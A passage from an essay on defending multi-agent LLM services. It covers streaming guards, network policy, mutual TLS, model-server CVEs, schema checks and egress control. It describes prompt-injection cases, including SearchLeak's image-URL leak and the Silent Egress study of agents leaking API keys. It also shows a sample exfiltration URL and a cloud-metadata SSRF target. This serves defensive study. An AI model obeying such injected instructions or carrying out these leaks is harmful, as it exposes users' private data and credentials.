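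Developers may still choose the faster mode because the safer one looks broken. AI SDK's troubleshooting page *Azure OpenAI Slow to Stream* describes text that arrives slowly and in big chunks. It relays users' reports that switching to the asynchronous filter helps. The stream becomes smoother because Azure no longer checks the text before displaying it.

Some gateways don't check streamed answers. TrueFoundry documents that its gateway skips output guards when an application requests streaming, because those guards need the complete text. The company suggests turning streaming off, checking the answer in the application after it ends, or relying on input guards alone. Input guards would not catch a scam address that the model learned in training. An operator could also test an output guard on non-streaming requests, see it work, and then have no protection in a live chat window that streams.

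Even within one product, how a streamed answer is handled can depend on which interface the application uses. Cloudflare's gateway has two. On one, the guard evaluates the streamed answer and logs the result, but the user still receives the whole answer. On the other, the gateway holds the answer until it is complete and returns it in one piece, so the application loses streaming. Portkey streams the answer normally and sends the guard's verdict in an extra chunk after the answer ends. The application then has to decide whether to retry, filter the answer or show a warning.

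A gateway that holds text before releasing it can also have gaps. According to *Guardrail Behavior*, the documentation for the AISIX gateway, AISIX holds a streamed answer in full or in windows, depending on the guard. It blocks answers that exceed its buffer, which is 262,144 bytes by default. But it does not scan the reasoning a model writes before its answer, and it passes on some kinds of message it doesn't recognise. If every output guard only monitors, the gateway releases the text immediately and checks it after the stream ends.

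An operator can find most of these gaps by adding a harmless address to the guard's blocklist, making the assistant repeat it in a streamed answer, and checking whether the address reaches the browser.

### SearchLeak and the late sanitiser

Retracting an answer cannot undo a request that the browser has already sent. SearchLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that let data leave through images fetched by Bing, depended on this. Microsoft rated it critical and tracked it as CVE-2026-42824. Varonis, which discovered the flaw, describes it in *SearchLeak* (2026) as a race between displaying the answer and making it safe.

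Copilot had a sanitiser that turned HTML in an answer into plain text, so that the browser would show the code instead of acting on it. But the sanitiser ran only after Copilot had finished generating the answer. Until then, the browser interpreted the HTML as it arrived and could request an image straight away. By the time the sanitiser turned the image into text, the browser had already sent out the private data in the image's address.

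The attack also depended on a crafted link, whose text Copilot treated as an instruction, and on Bing being a permitted image source. Varonis argues that all three weaknesses were necessary, so sanitising the answer in time would have stopped this attack.

Varonis recommends sanitising text when the browser displays it. In the shop's chat window, the front end could insert all streamed text as plain text and create a link or image only after the complete address has passed the guard. This would also protect the customer if the model's answer broke off halfway.

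### Guards trained to judge unfinished text

A guard trained on complete answers does worse on partial ones. Li and colleagues measured this drop in performance on a set of 29,000 prompts and answers, where the harmful answers included material such as instructions for crimes. They trained several guards on complete answers, then tested each one on both complete and partial answers. In the partial test, the guard judged the answer again after every new token and stopped it once a set number of tokens had looked harmful.

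They also built guards for streaming, which they call streaming content monitors. To create the training data, they had a language model label each sentence as harmful or harmless, then marked the nouns, verbs and adjectives in harmful sentences as harmful. They trained each monitor to score both single tokens and whole answers, and penalised it if it scored an answer as harmful but none of the answer's tokens as harmful. In service, the monitor uses only the token scores to decide when to stop.

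Each cell below gives the detection rate, followed by the false-positive rate:

| Base model | Ordinary guard, complete answers | Ordinary guard, partial answers | Streaming monitor, partial answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| ModernBERT, 0.4 billion parameters | 96.0% / 3.1% | 96.5% / 9.3% | not built |
| Qwen2.5, 0.5 billion | 94.5% / 3.2% | 90.6% / 12.4% | 95.2% / 3.9% |
| Qwen2.5, 1.5 billion | 98.3% / 1.9% | 98.7% / 20.8% | 98.0% / 2.1% |
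| Qwen2.5, 7 billion | 92.3% / 6.7% | 98.4% / 36.8% | 97.2% / 2.3% |

Most of the loss comes from false alarms. When the ordinary guards read partial text, they still caught most harmful answers but stopped many more good ones, partly because judging an answer hundreds of times gives a guard more chances to make a mistake. The 1.5-billion-parameter guard's F1, averaged over harmful and harmless answers, fell from 98.2 to 87.8, while the streaming monitor of the same size scored 97.9. The largest monitor beat the guard that read complete answers, but that guard did unusually badly for its size, so the comparison is weak evidence that partial text is enough.

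An operator can reduce false alarms by setting the monitor to stop an answer only after it detects more harmful tokens. When Li and colleagues raised this threshold, precision rose from about 84% to 98%, but the detection rate fell from about 99% to 91%. Even at 2.1%, the lowest false-positive rate among the streaming monitors, a monitor would cut off about 21,000 of the shop's good answers a day.

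On average, the monitor stopped a harmful answer after 18% of its tokens. The harmful answers in the collection average about 416 words, so a customer would typically see about 75 words before the cutoff if the front end released text immediately. Just under a fifth of the harmful answers ran past the 30% mark before the monitor stopped them.

Such early detection can be misleading. *HaloGuard 2.0* (2026) points out that in typical test collections nearly every harmful answer is harmful from its first token. A guard can score well on these by judging the user's prompt and ignoring the answer. In the collection Li and colleagues used, flagging every answer to a harmful prompt would catch 98.8% of the harmful answers but also flag 37.5% of the harmless ones. Their monitors had far fewer false alarms, so they must have learned something from the answers themselves.

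*HaloGuard 2.0* also distinguishes two errors that only a streaming guard can make. It can stop an answer that would have remained safe, or recognise harm only after the user has seen it. *FreoStream* (2026) attributes similar problems to guards not seeing the rest of the answer. Such guards tend to block sensitive but harmless content and become weaker against jailbreaks, which are prompts designed to get around a model's safety training.

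A guard has more context if it waits for complete sentences. *SentGuard* (2026) checks each sentence while the model writes the next, and it releases only text that has passed. *SentGuard* argues that checking token by token leads to unstable decisions, because a fragment of a sentence means little by itself. Releasing whole sentences also lets the customer read a steady series of complete thoughts instead of bursts that break off at an arbitrary token.

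A guard can also predict where an answer is going and stop the model before the harmful part appears. The guard in *Predict, Don't React* (2026) does this by estimating how harmful the likely continuations of a partial answer are. In its developers' tests, it intervened in time more often than a comparable guard trained to find the point where harm begins, and it missed fewer unsafe answers.

Prediction is much less useful for links, which a streaming guard still has to hold back until it can look up the whole address.

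## Filtering traffic between components

Most of the text in the refund example never reaches the customer's screen. The support agent exchanges messages with the model, the document store, the tool server and the billing agent, and any of those messages can carry an injection or private data. The shop can limit which components may connect, and it can inspect the messages sent between those that do.

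### Closing connections that nobody needs

A private network blocks outsiders but doesn't restrict the components inside it. Google Cloud notes in its design for multi-agent applications that once an agent's traffic is on the private network, it can reach any destination the network has a route to. The operator has to add firewall rules to limit which destinations it can reach.

Kubernetes, the most common system for running cloud software in containers, is just as open by default. It groups containers into pods, each normally with its own network address. According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, every pod can connect to every other until someone writes a policy. The usual remedy is default deny, in which the operator first writes a policy that applies to every pod and permits no connections, then allows the necessary ones one at a time. Both the sender's outgoing rules and the receiver's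 incoming rules must permit a connection.

Suppose the shop runs its own model server and keeps its orders in a database that only the tool server uses. Its permitted connections might be these:

| Caller | Destination | Permitted requests |
|---|---|---|
| Front end | Gateway | Send a customer's question |
| Gateway | Support agent | Deliver the question |
| Support agent | Gateway | Call the model, search documents, look up an order, ask for a refund |
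| Gateway | Document store | Search |
| Gateway | Model server | Generate text |
| Gateway | Tool server | Look up an order, pay a refund |
| Gateway | Billing agent | Deliver a refund request |
| Billing agent | Gateway | Call the model, look up an order, pay a refund |
| Tool server | Order database | Read orders, record refunds |

Eight components could form 56 connections, counting each direction separately. The shop needs nine of them and can refuse the other 47. It also needs to allow the lookups that turn component names into addresses. An attacker who takes over the document store can't open a connection from it to the order database, whatever code they run there.

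Kubernetes relies on a separate network plugin to enforce network policies. If the installed plugin doesn't support them, Kubernetes still accepts the policy, but it has no effect. A pod that starts before the plugin has processed a new policy may run unprotected for a while. The plugin also determines whether a new rule closes connections that are already open.

A small mistake can also make a policy admit more traffic than intended. In an example from the Kubernetes documentation, a rule should admit only pods that have a certain label and belong to a certain group. One extra hyphen makes it admit every pod in that group, plus every pod with the label in the policy's own group. Since network policies can't log the connections they refuse, an operator should try some forbidden connections from inside each pod and confirm that they fail.

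According to the Kubernetes documentation, a network policy also cannot force internal traffic through a common gateway. It can block the support agent's direct connection to the tool server, but the agent must be configured to send its requests to the gateway.

### Proving which component is calling

A packet filter identifies components by address, and Kubernetes regularly reassigns addresses to new pods. Mutual TLS provides better proof of identity by requiring both the caller and the server to present certificates showing who they are. Ordinary TLS, the encryption behind "https", requires a certificate only from the server.

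The shop doesn't have to build this into each component. Istio, an open-source "service mesh", places a sidecar beside each one, which is a proxy that handles all of that component's traffic. Istio's *Security* describes how a request travels:

1. Istio redirects the caller's outgoing request to the caller's own sidecar.
2. That sidecar and the one beside the destination exchange certificates. The caller's sidecar also checks that the identity in the destination's certificate is authorised to run the service it asked for.
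3. The two sidecars open an encrypted connection.
4. The destination's sidecar checks whether the caller may make this request, and if so passes it to the component.

The second check protects against an attacker who uses one component's stolen certificate to impersonate another component. Suppose an attacker steals a test program's certificate and redirects the gateway's searches to a fake document store. The fake store can prove that it is the test program, but the test program isn't authorized to run the document store, so the gateway's sidecar refuses to send the search. According to Istio, this check doesn't protect traffic other than web requests, such as a database connection, from falsified address lookups.

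Once the destination's sidecar has decrypted the request, it can apply rules to the request's method and path. In Istio's notation, the rule for the model server could be:

```yaml
action: ALLOW
rules:
- from:
  - source:
      principals: ["cluster.local/ns/shop/sa/gateway"]
  to:
  - operation:
      methods: ["POST"]
      paths: ["/v1/chat/completions"]
```

This lets the gateway request text from the model server but nothing else. A packet filter couldn't enforce the same rule, because requests to generate text and requests to replace the model's weights may use the same address and port.

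Istio leaves these restrictions off by default. It accepts unencrypted traffic alongside mutual TLS, so that operators can move components over gradually, and it allows every request to a component that has no authorisation policy. Operators need to set strict mode and write the rules. They should also check that each rule suits the traffic, because Istio ignores conditions on methods and paths when a component uses a plain TCP protocol, as many databases do.

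Mutual TLS identifies only the direct caller. In the table above, every order lookup and refund reaches the tool server from the gateway, so the certificate the tool server receives doesn't show which agent made the request. The gateway receives the agent's own certificate, so it must be the one to refuse a refund call from the support agent. The certificate also doesn't identify the customer. The front end can attach a signed token that names her, and the tool server can then check that she placed the order in question. Istio can verify such tokens, but it accepts requests without a token unless a separate rule requires one.

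Each layer sees more than the one below it:

| Check | What it sees | What it can stop | What it can't recognise |
|---|---|---|---|
| Packet filter | Addresses, ports and protocol | The document store connecting to the order database | A forbidden request on a permitted connection |
| Proxy that ends encryption | The caller's identity, the method, the path and the message | The support agent calling the refund tool | A false statement in a permitted request |
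| Schema check | Field names, types and allowed values | An extra field containing a home address | A valid value chosen by an attacker |

None of these checks examines what a message means. The delivery record with the courier's injected note passes them because it comes from the right component, over an encrypted connection, in reply to a permitted request.

### Traffic inside a distributed model server

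The table lists the model server as one component, but a large model may need several machines, each with several accelerators (the processors that do the model's arithmetic). These machines exchange far more data than the rest of the shop's system. The traffic has three main parts. Worker programs send messages to coordinate their shares of each calculation. Machines may pass on the key-value cache, the stored intermediate results for text the model has already read, so that one machine can read the prompt and another can write the answer. Programs also send each other serialised objects, which are data structures converted to bytes.

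The projects that supply this software state that they do not protect the traffic. vLLM is a widely used open-source model server, and its *Security* calls all communication between its machines "insecure by default". Much of that communication relies on PyTorch, a library for building and running neural networks. PyTorch's *SECURITY.md* explains that, for speed, the library's distributed features send messages unencrypted, accept connections from anywhere and run the work they receive without checks. Ray, a framework for spreading programs over many machines, can start and manage vLLM's workers. Its *Security* warns that Ray lets any client run arbitrary code. There is little reason to doubt these statements, since the developers are describing weaknesses in their own products.

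| Channel | Protection by default | What the project recommends |
|---|---|---|
| PyTorch worker coordination | No encryption and no check of the caller | Internal networks only |
| vLLM cache transfer between machines | None | An isolated network and firewall rules |
| vLLM's web interface | None, and the optional key covers only some paths | A proxy that permits only the necessary paths |
| vLLM's gRPC interface, a second way to send requests | Switched off, and it has no encryption or authentication when on | Access from trusted machines only |
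| Ray's dashboard and job interfaces | Depends on the version | An isolated network, plus a token |

Filtering matters on a single machine too, because vLLM still uses PyTorch's distributed features there. One of them, a small server that workers use to find each other, listens on every network interface by default, so any host that can reach the machine may be able to connect to that server.

vLLM's API key can also give false confidence. With a key set, a request to `/v1/chat/completions` must include it. But `/invocations` performs the same work without the key, `/pause` stops the server from generating, and `/update_weights`, meant for training, can change the model's behaviour. The documentation even contradicts itself about one path, `/inference/v1/generate`, which it lists first as protected by the key and later as a way around it. A proxy rule like the one for the gateway closes all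 of these paths at once. Afterwards, the shop should request each path without a key to confirm that the proxy refuses it.

A request can also make the model server connect to other machines. Some models accept images, and a user may supply a URL for vLLM to fetch an image from. If the URL points to an internal service, the server may reach a service that the user could not reach directly. One common target is `169.254.169.254`, where cloud providers make a machine's settings, and often its credentials, available to it. vLLM can restrict these fetches to an allowlist of domains, and its documentation recommends disabling redirects, which could lead from an allowed domain to an internal address. The network policy should block these connections as well.

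Workers can receive secrets they don't need. When vLLM runs on several machines under the current version of its Ray executor, it copies nearly all environment variables, which often include passwords and cloud keys, from the main program to the workers. This is deliberate, because vLLM is designed for Ray clusters in which every machine is equally trusted. An operator who wants to keep a key on one machine has to add the variable's name to an exclusion list.

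The cache also leaks information between customers. If two prompts begin with the same text, vLLM can reuse the stored results from the first, and the second answer starts sooner. An attacker who shares the server can guess how someone else's prompt begins, send that guess, and time the reply to check it. The vLLM project cites research in which the delay distinguished right guesses from wrong ones almost perfectly, even for beginnings of only eight tokens. The fix for this flaw, CVE-2025-46570, is to attach a secret random value, called a salt, to each customer's requests, because vLLM shares cached results only between requests with the same salt. Different customers then can't reuse each other's results, so the server does more work. vLLM doesn't add a salt by default.

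### When receiving an object runs code

The most serious flaws in this traffic come from pickle, Python's built-in format for serialised objects. A pickled object can contain the name of a function and its arguments, and Python calls the function while it rebuilds the object. An attacker who can send bytes to a program that unpickles them can therefore run commands on the program's machine. Checking the rebuilt object is too late, because the command has already run.

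Several model servers shared this weakness because their developers had copied code. According to Oligo Security's *ShadowMQ*, researchers found in 2024 that Meta's Llama Stack used a function from the messaging library ZeroMQ that unpickles whatever it receives. They later found the same pattern in other projects, sometimes in files copied line for line. The Hacker News' *Researchers Find Serious AI Bugs* (2025) lists Nvidia's TensorRT-LLM, Microsoft's Sarathi-Serve, Modular's Max Server, vLLM and SGLang. In each, the connection that received the objects had no authentication.

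The entries below also include related flaws in PyTorch and Ray. OSV is a public database of vulnerabilities in open-source software.

| Flaw | What an attacker could reach | Affected software | Fix or remedy |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2024-50050 | Unpickling over ZeroMQ | Meta's Llama framework | Meta patched it in October 2024 |
| PYSEC-2026-2017 | Messages between vLLM machines over ZeroMQ | vLLM's older V0 engine, when it splits a model's calculations across several machines | No fix planned. The V1 engine is unaffected |
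| PYSEC-2026-567 | Control messages for cache transfer | vLLM's PyNcclPipe service | Restrict the service to a secured network |
| CVE-2024-48063 | PyTorch's features for calling code on other machines | PyTorch, including version 2.6.0 as packaged by Debian | None in Debian, which treats it as a non-issue |
| CVE-2025-62593 | Ray's interfaces, through a developer's browser | Ray before 2.52.0 | Upgrade to 2.52.0 or later |

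Two of these flaws are deliberately unfixed. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2017* rates the vLLM flaw's severity 8.0 out of 10. vLLM's maintainers decided against an invasive fix because the V0 engine had been off by default since version 0.8.0 and they thought few people used it across several machines. Debian's *CVE-2024-48063* accepts PyTorch's position that the affected features are for internal communication only. Both decisions are defensible if the network is isolated. If the document store or a tool server can reach the workers, an attacker who takes over one of those components can take over the model too.

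The cache-transfer flaw shows that isolation can fail even when an operator follows the instructions correctly. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-567*, vLLM's developers meant the service to be available only at the private address the operator supplied, but PyTorch opened it on every interface. The firewall therefore needs to block the port even when the program's own settings seem to restrict access.

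The last flaw in the table let a web page open in a developer's browser send requests to a Ray service that the browser could reach, and Ray runs the jobs it receives. Anyscale, the company behind Ray, says in *Ray CVE-2025-62593 KEV* that version 2.52.0 replaced a weak check for browser traffic with proper controls. ("KEV" is short for the US government's catalogue of known exploited vulnerabilities.) The same release introduced a token, a shared secret that a hostile page cannot read or guess. Saglam (2025) acknowledged in *Introducing Token-Based Authentication for Ray* that open-source Ray previously had no authentication on its dashboard or interfaces.

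Upgrading Ray to 2.52.0 didn't turn on token authentication. VulnCheck's *Anyscale Ray Token Authentication Disabled by Default Insecure Configuration* rates that default as a vulnerability in its own right, with a severity of 9.3. According to Ray's documentation, version 2.59 turns on token authentication for new local clusters, and 2.61 extends it to all clusters. In 2.59, a cluster that an operator starts by hand can still run unauthenticated, with only a warning, if no token exists.

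The token is also weaker evidence than a certificate. Every machine and client in a Ray cluster uses the same one, so it proves that a caller belongs to the cluster but not which component is calling. It doesn't expire, and anyone who can read unencrypted traffic can copy it. Ray therefore presents the token as an addition to an isolated network, and recommends separate clusters for work that must stay apart. Some commercial platforms set up part of this for the customer. Red Hat's *Implementing best practices* says OpenShift AI 3.0 applies network controls to Ray clusters by default, though this is the vendor's own account.

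Developers can also remove the underlying weakness by sending messages in a format such as JSON, which can represent text, numbers and lists but can't specify a function to call. A program that has to exchange Python objects can require a signature and verify it before unpickling anything. Neither measure stops someone listening on the network from reading the messages. To prevent that, vLLM's documentation suggests adding encryption from outside, for example with a sidecar that uses mutual TLS.

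### Direct links between accelerators

Encryption and proxies are hardest to add where the machines exchange the most data. Many clusters use remote direct memory access (RDMA), in which a network card copies data straight from one machine's memory into another's. RDMA is fast because neither machine's operating system handles the individual transfers. An ordinary firewall may therefore miss them, because it usually runs in the operating system and can inspect only the traffic that passes through it. A sidecar has the same problem, and routing every transfer through one would lose much of the speed.

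Kubernetes offers only limited help here. A default-deny policy is guaranteed to block only TCP, UDP and SCTP, and its effect on other protocols depends on the network plugin. Programs that need direct access to the network card may run on the host network, where they share the machine's address. According to Kubernetes, most plugins can't distinguish these programs from the machine itself, so rules written for pods don't apply to them.

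Rules for whole machines can fill part of the gap. Cilium's *Host Policies* describes how Cilium, a network plugin for Kubernetes, can restrict a machine's traffic by address and port. These rules still depend on software that handles the traffic. For the direct links, the switches and network cards have to keep traffic separate, or the links need a physical network that carries nothing else. The gateway's connection to the model server can then be the only way in from the rest of the shop's system, and the guards can be placed on that connection.

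### Checking the shape of a tool call

The guards at the gateway see messages as well as connections. The simplest check on a message is schema validation, which compares a tool call with a written description of its permitted fields and values. For an order lookup, the schema could allow one field, `order_id`, containing exactly seven digits. This call passes:

`{"order_id": "5530182"}`

Now suppose an injected instruction makes the model add the customer's address to the call:

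`{"order_id": "5530182", "comment": "14 Mill Lane"}`

The gateway rejects the second call because the schema has no `comment` field, so it doesn't need to recognise an address or detect an injection. But if the schema allowed a comment of 500 characters, that one field would let through the same call and most other things an attacker might want to send.

Developers can often replace free text with a short list of choices. The refund request needs an order number, an amount and a reason, and the reason could be "lost", "damaged" or "returned". The support agent then can't pass a paragraph of injected text to the billing agent, because no field has room for one. But unusual cases won't fit. If a customer's router arrived with someone else's name on it, a person would need to handle the refund.

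Some values shouldn't come from the model. If the model writes the customer's account number into each call, an injected instruction can change it to another customer's. The gateway can prevent this by overwriting the model's number with the one in the signed token. The tool server can also calculate the maximum refund from the order record. These checks compare a call with facts held elsewhere, so they can catch a false value even when its format is valid.

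FINOS's *AI Firewall Implementation and Management*, part of the same set of controls that requires all traffic to use gateways, says operators must manage such rules centrally and keep a version history. This helps when a tool changes. If a developer adds a field to the order tool and nobody updates the schema, the gateway will reject every new call, and the quickest fix is to turn validation off. With versioned rules, the shop can release the tool and its schema together and roll both back if something breaks.

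### Removing what the receiver doesn't need

Schema validation accepts or rejects a message, whereas minimisation removes parts of it. To tell the customer where her router is, the model needs only the delivery status and perhaps a date, but the tool server returns the full delivery record, including her home address and the courier's note. If the gateway passes on only the status and the date, the model never receives the address or the note, so it can't leak the address later and an injection in the note has no effect.

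This protection doesn't depend on the wording of the attack, but someone has to decide in advance which fields each task needs, and that decision will sometimes be wrong. For example, the courier's note may be the only record that the parcel is with a neighbour. The shop could let the assistant request the note in a separate call, and the gateway would then apply stricter rules to the rest of the conversation.

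Components can also send each other less text. When the support agent asks the billing agent for a refund, it might include the whole conversation in case some of it is useful. Any injected text in that conversation then enters the billing agent's input too.

When free text has to pass, the gateway can clean it. Ordinary code can remove invisible characters, comments hidden in a web page's source and any markup that the model doesn't need. This gets rid of common hiding places, but it doesn't remove an injection written as a plain sentence in the courier's note. A language model could rewrite the text and leave out anything that looks like an instruction, but that model also reads the injection and might obey it. It could also remove instructions that the customer wants, which are often the main content of the text, as in a router manual that tells her to hold the reset button for ten seconds.

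Two detectors described earlier act as firewalls at the same boundary, AgentRedGuard on tool responses and StepGuard on tool calls. Both let some attacks through, even though the attacks were not adapted to evade them. An adaptive attacker cannot exploit a field that the gateway has removed, so minimisation should come before a detector wherever the task allows it.

### Labels that travel with the text

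A label records where a piece of text came from or how sensitive it is, so later components can treat it accordingly. The gateway might mark the returns policy "written by staff" and the courier's note "written by an outsider". A rule could then require a person to approve any refund in a conversation that contains outside text.

The label has to be separate from the text. If the gateway wrote "trusted" above a passage, an attacker could type the same word into the courier's note. The gateway should store labels in fields that only it can set, and ordinary code should enforce the rules about them, because a model that sees a label may ignore it.

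Labels become harder to use once a model has mixed several texts, because nobody can reliably tell which words of its answer came from the courier's note and which from the policy. The cautious rule is to give the answer the least trusted label of anything the model read. Under this rule, an assistant that reads customers' questions all day produces almost entirely untrusted text, and requiring approval for all untrusted text would send every refund to a person. The shop can limit this by starting each task with a fresh conversation and by using fixed fields, such as the list of refund reasons, which can't contain text written by an attacker.

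In *Autonomous Topology Mutation*, Sidik, Levi and Kimhi (2026) tested sensitivity labels in a system that detects an overloaded agent and splits it into two specialised ones while it is running. Before the split, software gives each item in the old agent's memory a privacy level from 0 to 4. An item goes only to a new agent that needs it, and an item at level 3 or 4 can go to at most one, even if both could use it. Neither new agent can receive a tool that the old one lacked.

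Over 720 runs with DeepSeek-V3, the full system reduced detected exposures of memory at level 3 or above from 2.0 per task to none. The researchers counted exposures with a classifier built on written patterns, so a secret that matched no pattern would have both received a low label and escaped the count. The main test used stand-in tools that returned fixed results, and the researchers measured exposure rather than resistance to injection.

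The rule may also withhold too much. The procedure that Sidik and colleagues print gives neither new agent a highly sensitive item that both need, although the accompanying text allows one of them to have it. If that item were the customer's address, neither agent could finish its work. The shop would do better to keep the address in the order database and let each agent request a specific action, such as printing a shipping label, without seeing the address.

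### How an injection spreads between agents

An injected instruction can tell an agent to do something and to repeat the instruction in its output. If the courier's note does this, the support agent copies the text into its refund request, and the billing agent reads it there and may copy it into its next message. The attacker needed access only to a field in a delivery record. Every later message comes from one of the shop's own agents, with a valid certificate.

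A rough calculation shows when this becomes an epidemic. Suppose *k* agents read each compromised agent's output, each has a chance *q* of obeying the injection and passing it on, and a guard stops a share *D* of the infected messages. On average, one compromised agent then compromises

*R* = *kq*(1 − *D*)

others. If *R* is above 1, the injection tends to keep spreading. If it is below 1, the spread dies out, after reaching an average of 1/(1 − *R*) agents in total. With five readers and a 40% chance of obeying, *R* is 2 without a guard. A guard that stops 60% of infected messages lowers it to 0.8, for an average of five compromised agents. One that stops 80% lowers it to 0.4, for fewer than two.

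The calculation assumes that the guard has an independent chance of catching each copy, but identical copies will usually get the same verdict. An injection that gets past a detector once will probably get past it at every later step, so the real outcome is closer to all or nothing than the average implies. Using different kinds of guard between different agents would help, as long as they don't make the same mistakes.

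Restricting connections is more dependable because it limits *k* directly. In the shop, the support agent can message only one other agent, so an injection that arrives through it can't reach dozens. The document store is the exception, because if the agents write summaries of their conversations there, injected text can end up in a summary and return in any later conversation that retrieves it. It could reach thousands of future conversations on that topic. The shop should keep agents' own writing out of the store, or label it so that the assistant doesn't treat it as policy.

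### Comparing an agent's output with its input

A guard can look for copied text without deciding whether that text is an attack. In a simple version, the gateway keeps the outside text that the support agent has read and splits it into overlapping runs of eight words. A courier's note of 60 words has 53 such runs. If any of these runs appear in a message from the support agent to the billing agent, the gateway removes the copied passage or holds the message for review.

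This works against unfamiliar wording because the guard needs no examples of earlier attacks. An injection that spreads by repeating itself has to reproduce enough of its text to work on the next agent, and the guard detects that repetition. The check also takes little compute because it only compares strings of words.

Uncompromised agents also copy text. A support agent may quote a customer's complaint so that the billing agent can judge it, and an assistant that forwards emails mostly copies text. Comparing the output only with text from outsiders avoids alarms when an agent quotes the shop's own policy, but the check will still flag some legitimate quotations. It therefore works better for messages that should be short and factual than for those meant to pass on someone's words.

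An attacker can also defeat exact comparison by asking the agent to reword or encode the instruction before passing it on. A guard that compares meaning could catch the reworded version, but it would raise more false alarms because a faithful summary of a document also resembles the document in meaning. Checks for copying help against text that spreads from agent to agent, but not against an injection that does harm without copying itself. If the courier's note persuades the support agent to request a refund that nobody is owed, the request may consist entirely of new words.

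### A valid message can still be false

Suppose the deception succeeds, and the support agent asks the billing agent to refund $89 for a parcel it says was lost, although the parcel arrived yesterday. The request comes from the right component over mutual TLS. The path is on the list of permitted paths, the order number has seven digits, the reason is one of the three permitted words, and nothing in the message copies the courier's note. The request passes every check so far because each one examines only the sender or the form of the message, and none verifies that the parcel was lost.

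This is the best objection to relying on traffic filtering, and stricter schemas don't resolve it. Authentication can even make the problem worse if the billing agent's developers treat a verified sender as a reliable one. A certificate proves only that the message came from the support agent, not who wrote the text that the support agent had just read.

The checks do limit the attacker to making a false claim about one real order, in three fields. Without them, one injected note could lead to a payment of any amount to any account, or a command to the model server. The billing agent can test such a narrow claim without a language model. Ordinary code can look up the order, find that the courier delivered the parcel yesterday, and refuse the refund.

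## Controlling what leaves the network

The shop also needs connections to the outside world, which the rules for internal connections don't cover. Suppose its tool server looks up parcels on the courier's website, and its support agent is allowed to open public help pages. An injected instruction could cause either one to send private data out over its connection. Egress control limits where such connections can go and what they can carry.

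### The path of an outgoing request

Suppose an injected instruction makes the tool server add the customer's street address to a tracking request:

`https://courier.example/track?ref=8841907&note=14+Mill+Lane`

In a network with full egress control, the request goes through four steps:

1. The tool server looks up `courier.example` in the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of names and numeric addresses. A DNS filter answers if its rules permit the name and refuses otherwise.
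2. The tool server connects to a forward proxy, a program that makes outside connections on behalf of the components. A firewall drops every outgoing connection that doesn't come from the proxy.
3. The proxy compares the destination with an allowlist.
4. Content inspection searches the request for secrets, such as passwords or home addresses. If it finds none, the proxy sends the request on.

A DNS filter is a weak defence by itself, because a program that already has an IP address can connect without looking up a name. The firewall in step 2 covers this case.

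A DNS lookup can also leak data, even if no connection follows. If the shop's DNS server has no record of a name, it forwards the query, which can reach a server run by the domain's owner, who can then read any private text in the name. The filter therefore has to refuse forbidden names before forwarding anything. It should use an allowlist, because a blocklist would miss new domains. The list can be very short for most components, since the forward proxy can look up outside names for them. The tool server, for example, then needs to look up only the proxy.

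### What each check can read under encryption

Nearly all web traffic is encrypted, so most of these checks can read only part of the request:

| Check | What it can read | What stays hidden |
|---|---|---|
| DNS filter | `courier.example` and the type of record requested | Everything after the name |
| Firewall | Numeric addresses, ports and the amount of data | The path and the content |
| Forward proxy without decryption | `courier.example`, the port, the time and the amount of data | `/track?ref=8841907&note=14+Mill+Lane` and anything in the body of the request |
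| Forward proxy with decryption | The whole request and the whole reply | The meaning of text that the sender encoded or encrypted beforehand |

The proxy can read the host name because the tool server has to include it in the connection request. After that, the proxy relays encrypted data that it can't read. It can enforce a list of domains, but it can't apply OpenAI's rule that an exact URL must already be public, and it can't detect the customer's street in the data.

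Even without decryption, the proxy can stop some redirects. If `courier.example` redirects the tool server to `attacker.example`, the tool server has to request a second connection through the proxy, which blocks it. This partly addresses OpenAI's objection to domain lists, though a permitted site such as webhook.site can still expose the data it receives.

Programs can also encrypt their DNS lookups and send them to a public DNS service over an ordinary web connection. These lookups bypass the shop's own filter, so the firewall and proxy also have to block public DNS services.

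### Decrypting the traffic

To read the whole request, the proxy has to take the place of the website at the far end of the encrypted connection:

1. The operator creates a signing certificate and configures every component to trust it.
2. When the tool server asks for `courier.example`, the proxy makes a certificate for that name and signs it.
3. The tool server accepts the certificate and sends its encrypted request to the proxy.
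4. The proxy decrypts the request and checks it. If the request passes, the proxy opens a second encrypted connection to the real site.

The shop can then write much narrower rules. It could permit requests to `/track` only if they contain a seven-digit `ref` and nothing else, much as a schema restricts tool calls. It could let the agent read pages on a site but not upload anything. The proxy can also pass the site's reply to a detector that looks for injected instructions.

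Decryption also creates risks. The proxy handles every password and home address in readable form, so an attacker who takes it over can collect them all. Someone who steals the signing key could impersonate any website to the shop's components. The components can no longer check the real site's certificate, so the proxy has to do it. Some programs accept only one particular certificate, so they stop working when the proxy presents its own. The usual fix is to exempt their traffic from decryption, which leaves it uninspected.

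The shop can avoid some of this by inspecting requests earlier, at the gateway, where tool calls are not yet encrypted. The gateway can also identify which conversation a call belongs to. Decrypting traffic at the exit is most useful for components that build their own requests, such as an agent that writes and runs code.

### Leaks that the answer doesn't show

Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, measured how often an agent leaks data when nothing controls its outgoing requests. The researchers, who work at eBay, built an agent that automatically loads any web address in the user's message and adds the page's text to the model's input. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The researchers placed an injected instruction in the page's title, description, body or link text. In the example they print, the instruction is disguised as a required connectivity check and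 directs the agent to include the user's API key, a password for software, in a web request.

The researchers ran a server in place of the attacker's and recorded what it received, so they could count leaks from network traffic instead of judging the agent's answers. They varied where the instruction was placed, whether the page address redirected, and whether the instruction asked for one request or several. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

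Data reached the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the user saw a harmless answer. Redirects made almost no difference: data leaked in 210 of 240 runs without them and 213 of 240 with them. When the instruction asked for a single request, the attack worked in 238 of 240 runs.

The 95% figure matters more because it reflects how agents are built. The agent leaks the key through a tool call and writes its summary separately, so the key never reaches a guard that reads only the summary. A guard on tool calls would at least receive the request containing the key. The researchers did not test a classifier or a language-model judge on tool calls, so the study doesn't show that detectors in general would miss these attacks.

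The 88.1% figure is harder to apply elsewhere. All the runs used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about 7 billion parameters. The researchers put the secrets directly into its input, gave it a minimal system prompt (the operator's standing instructions) and didn't clean the page text. They describe this set-up as favourable to the attacker, but they also call the success rates a lower bound, because the injected text was simple and a better attack might work more often. Both points are fair, so the rate for a real service could be higher or lower.

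Lan and colleagues also suggest that stronger models may be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. They did not test stronger models, which may also be better at refusing.

### The defence test

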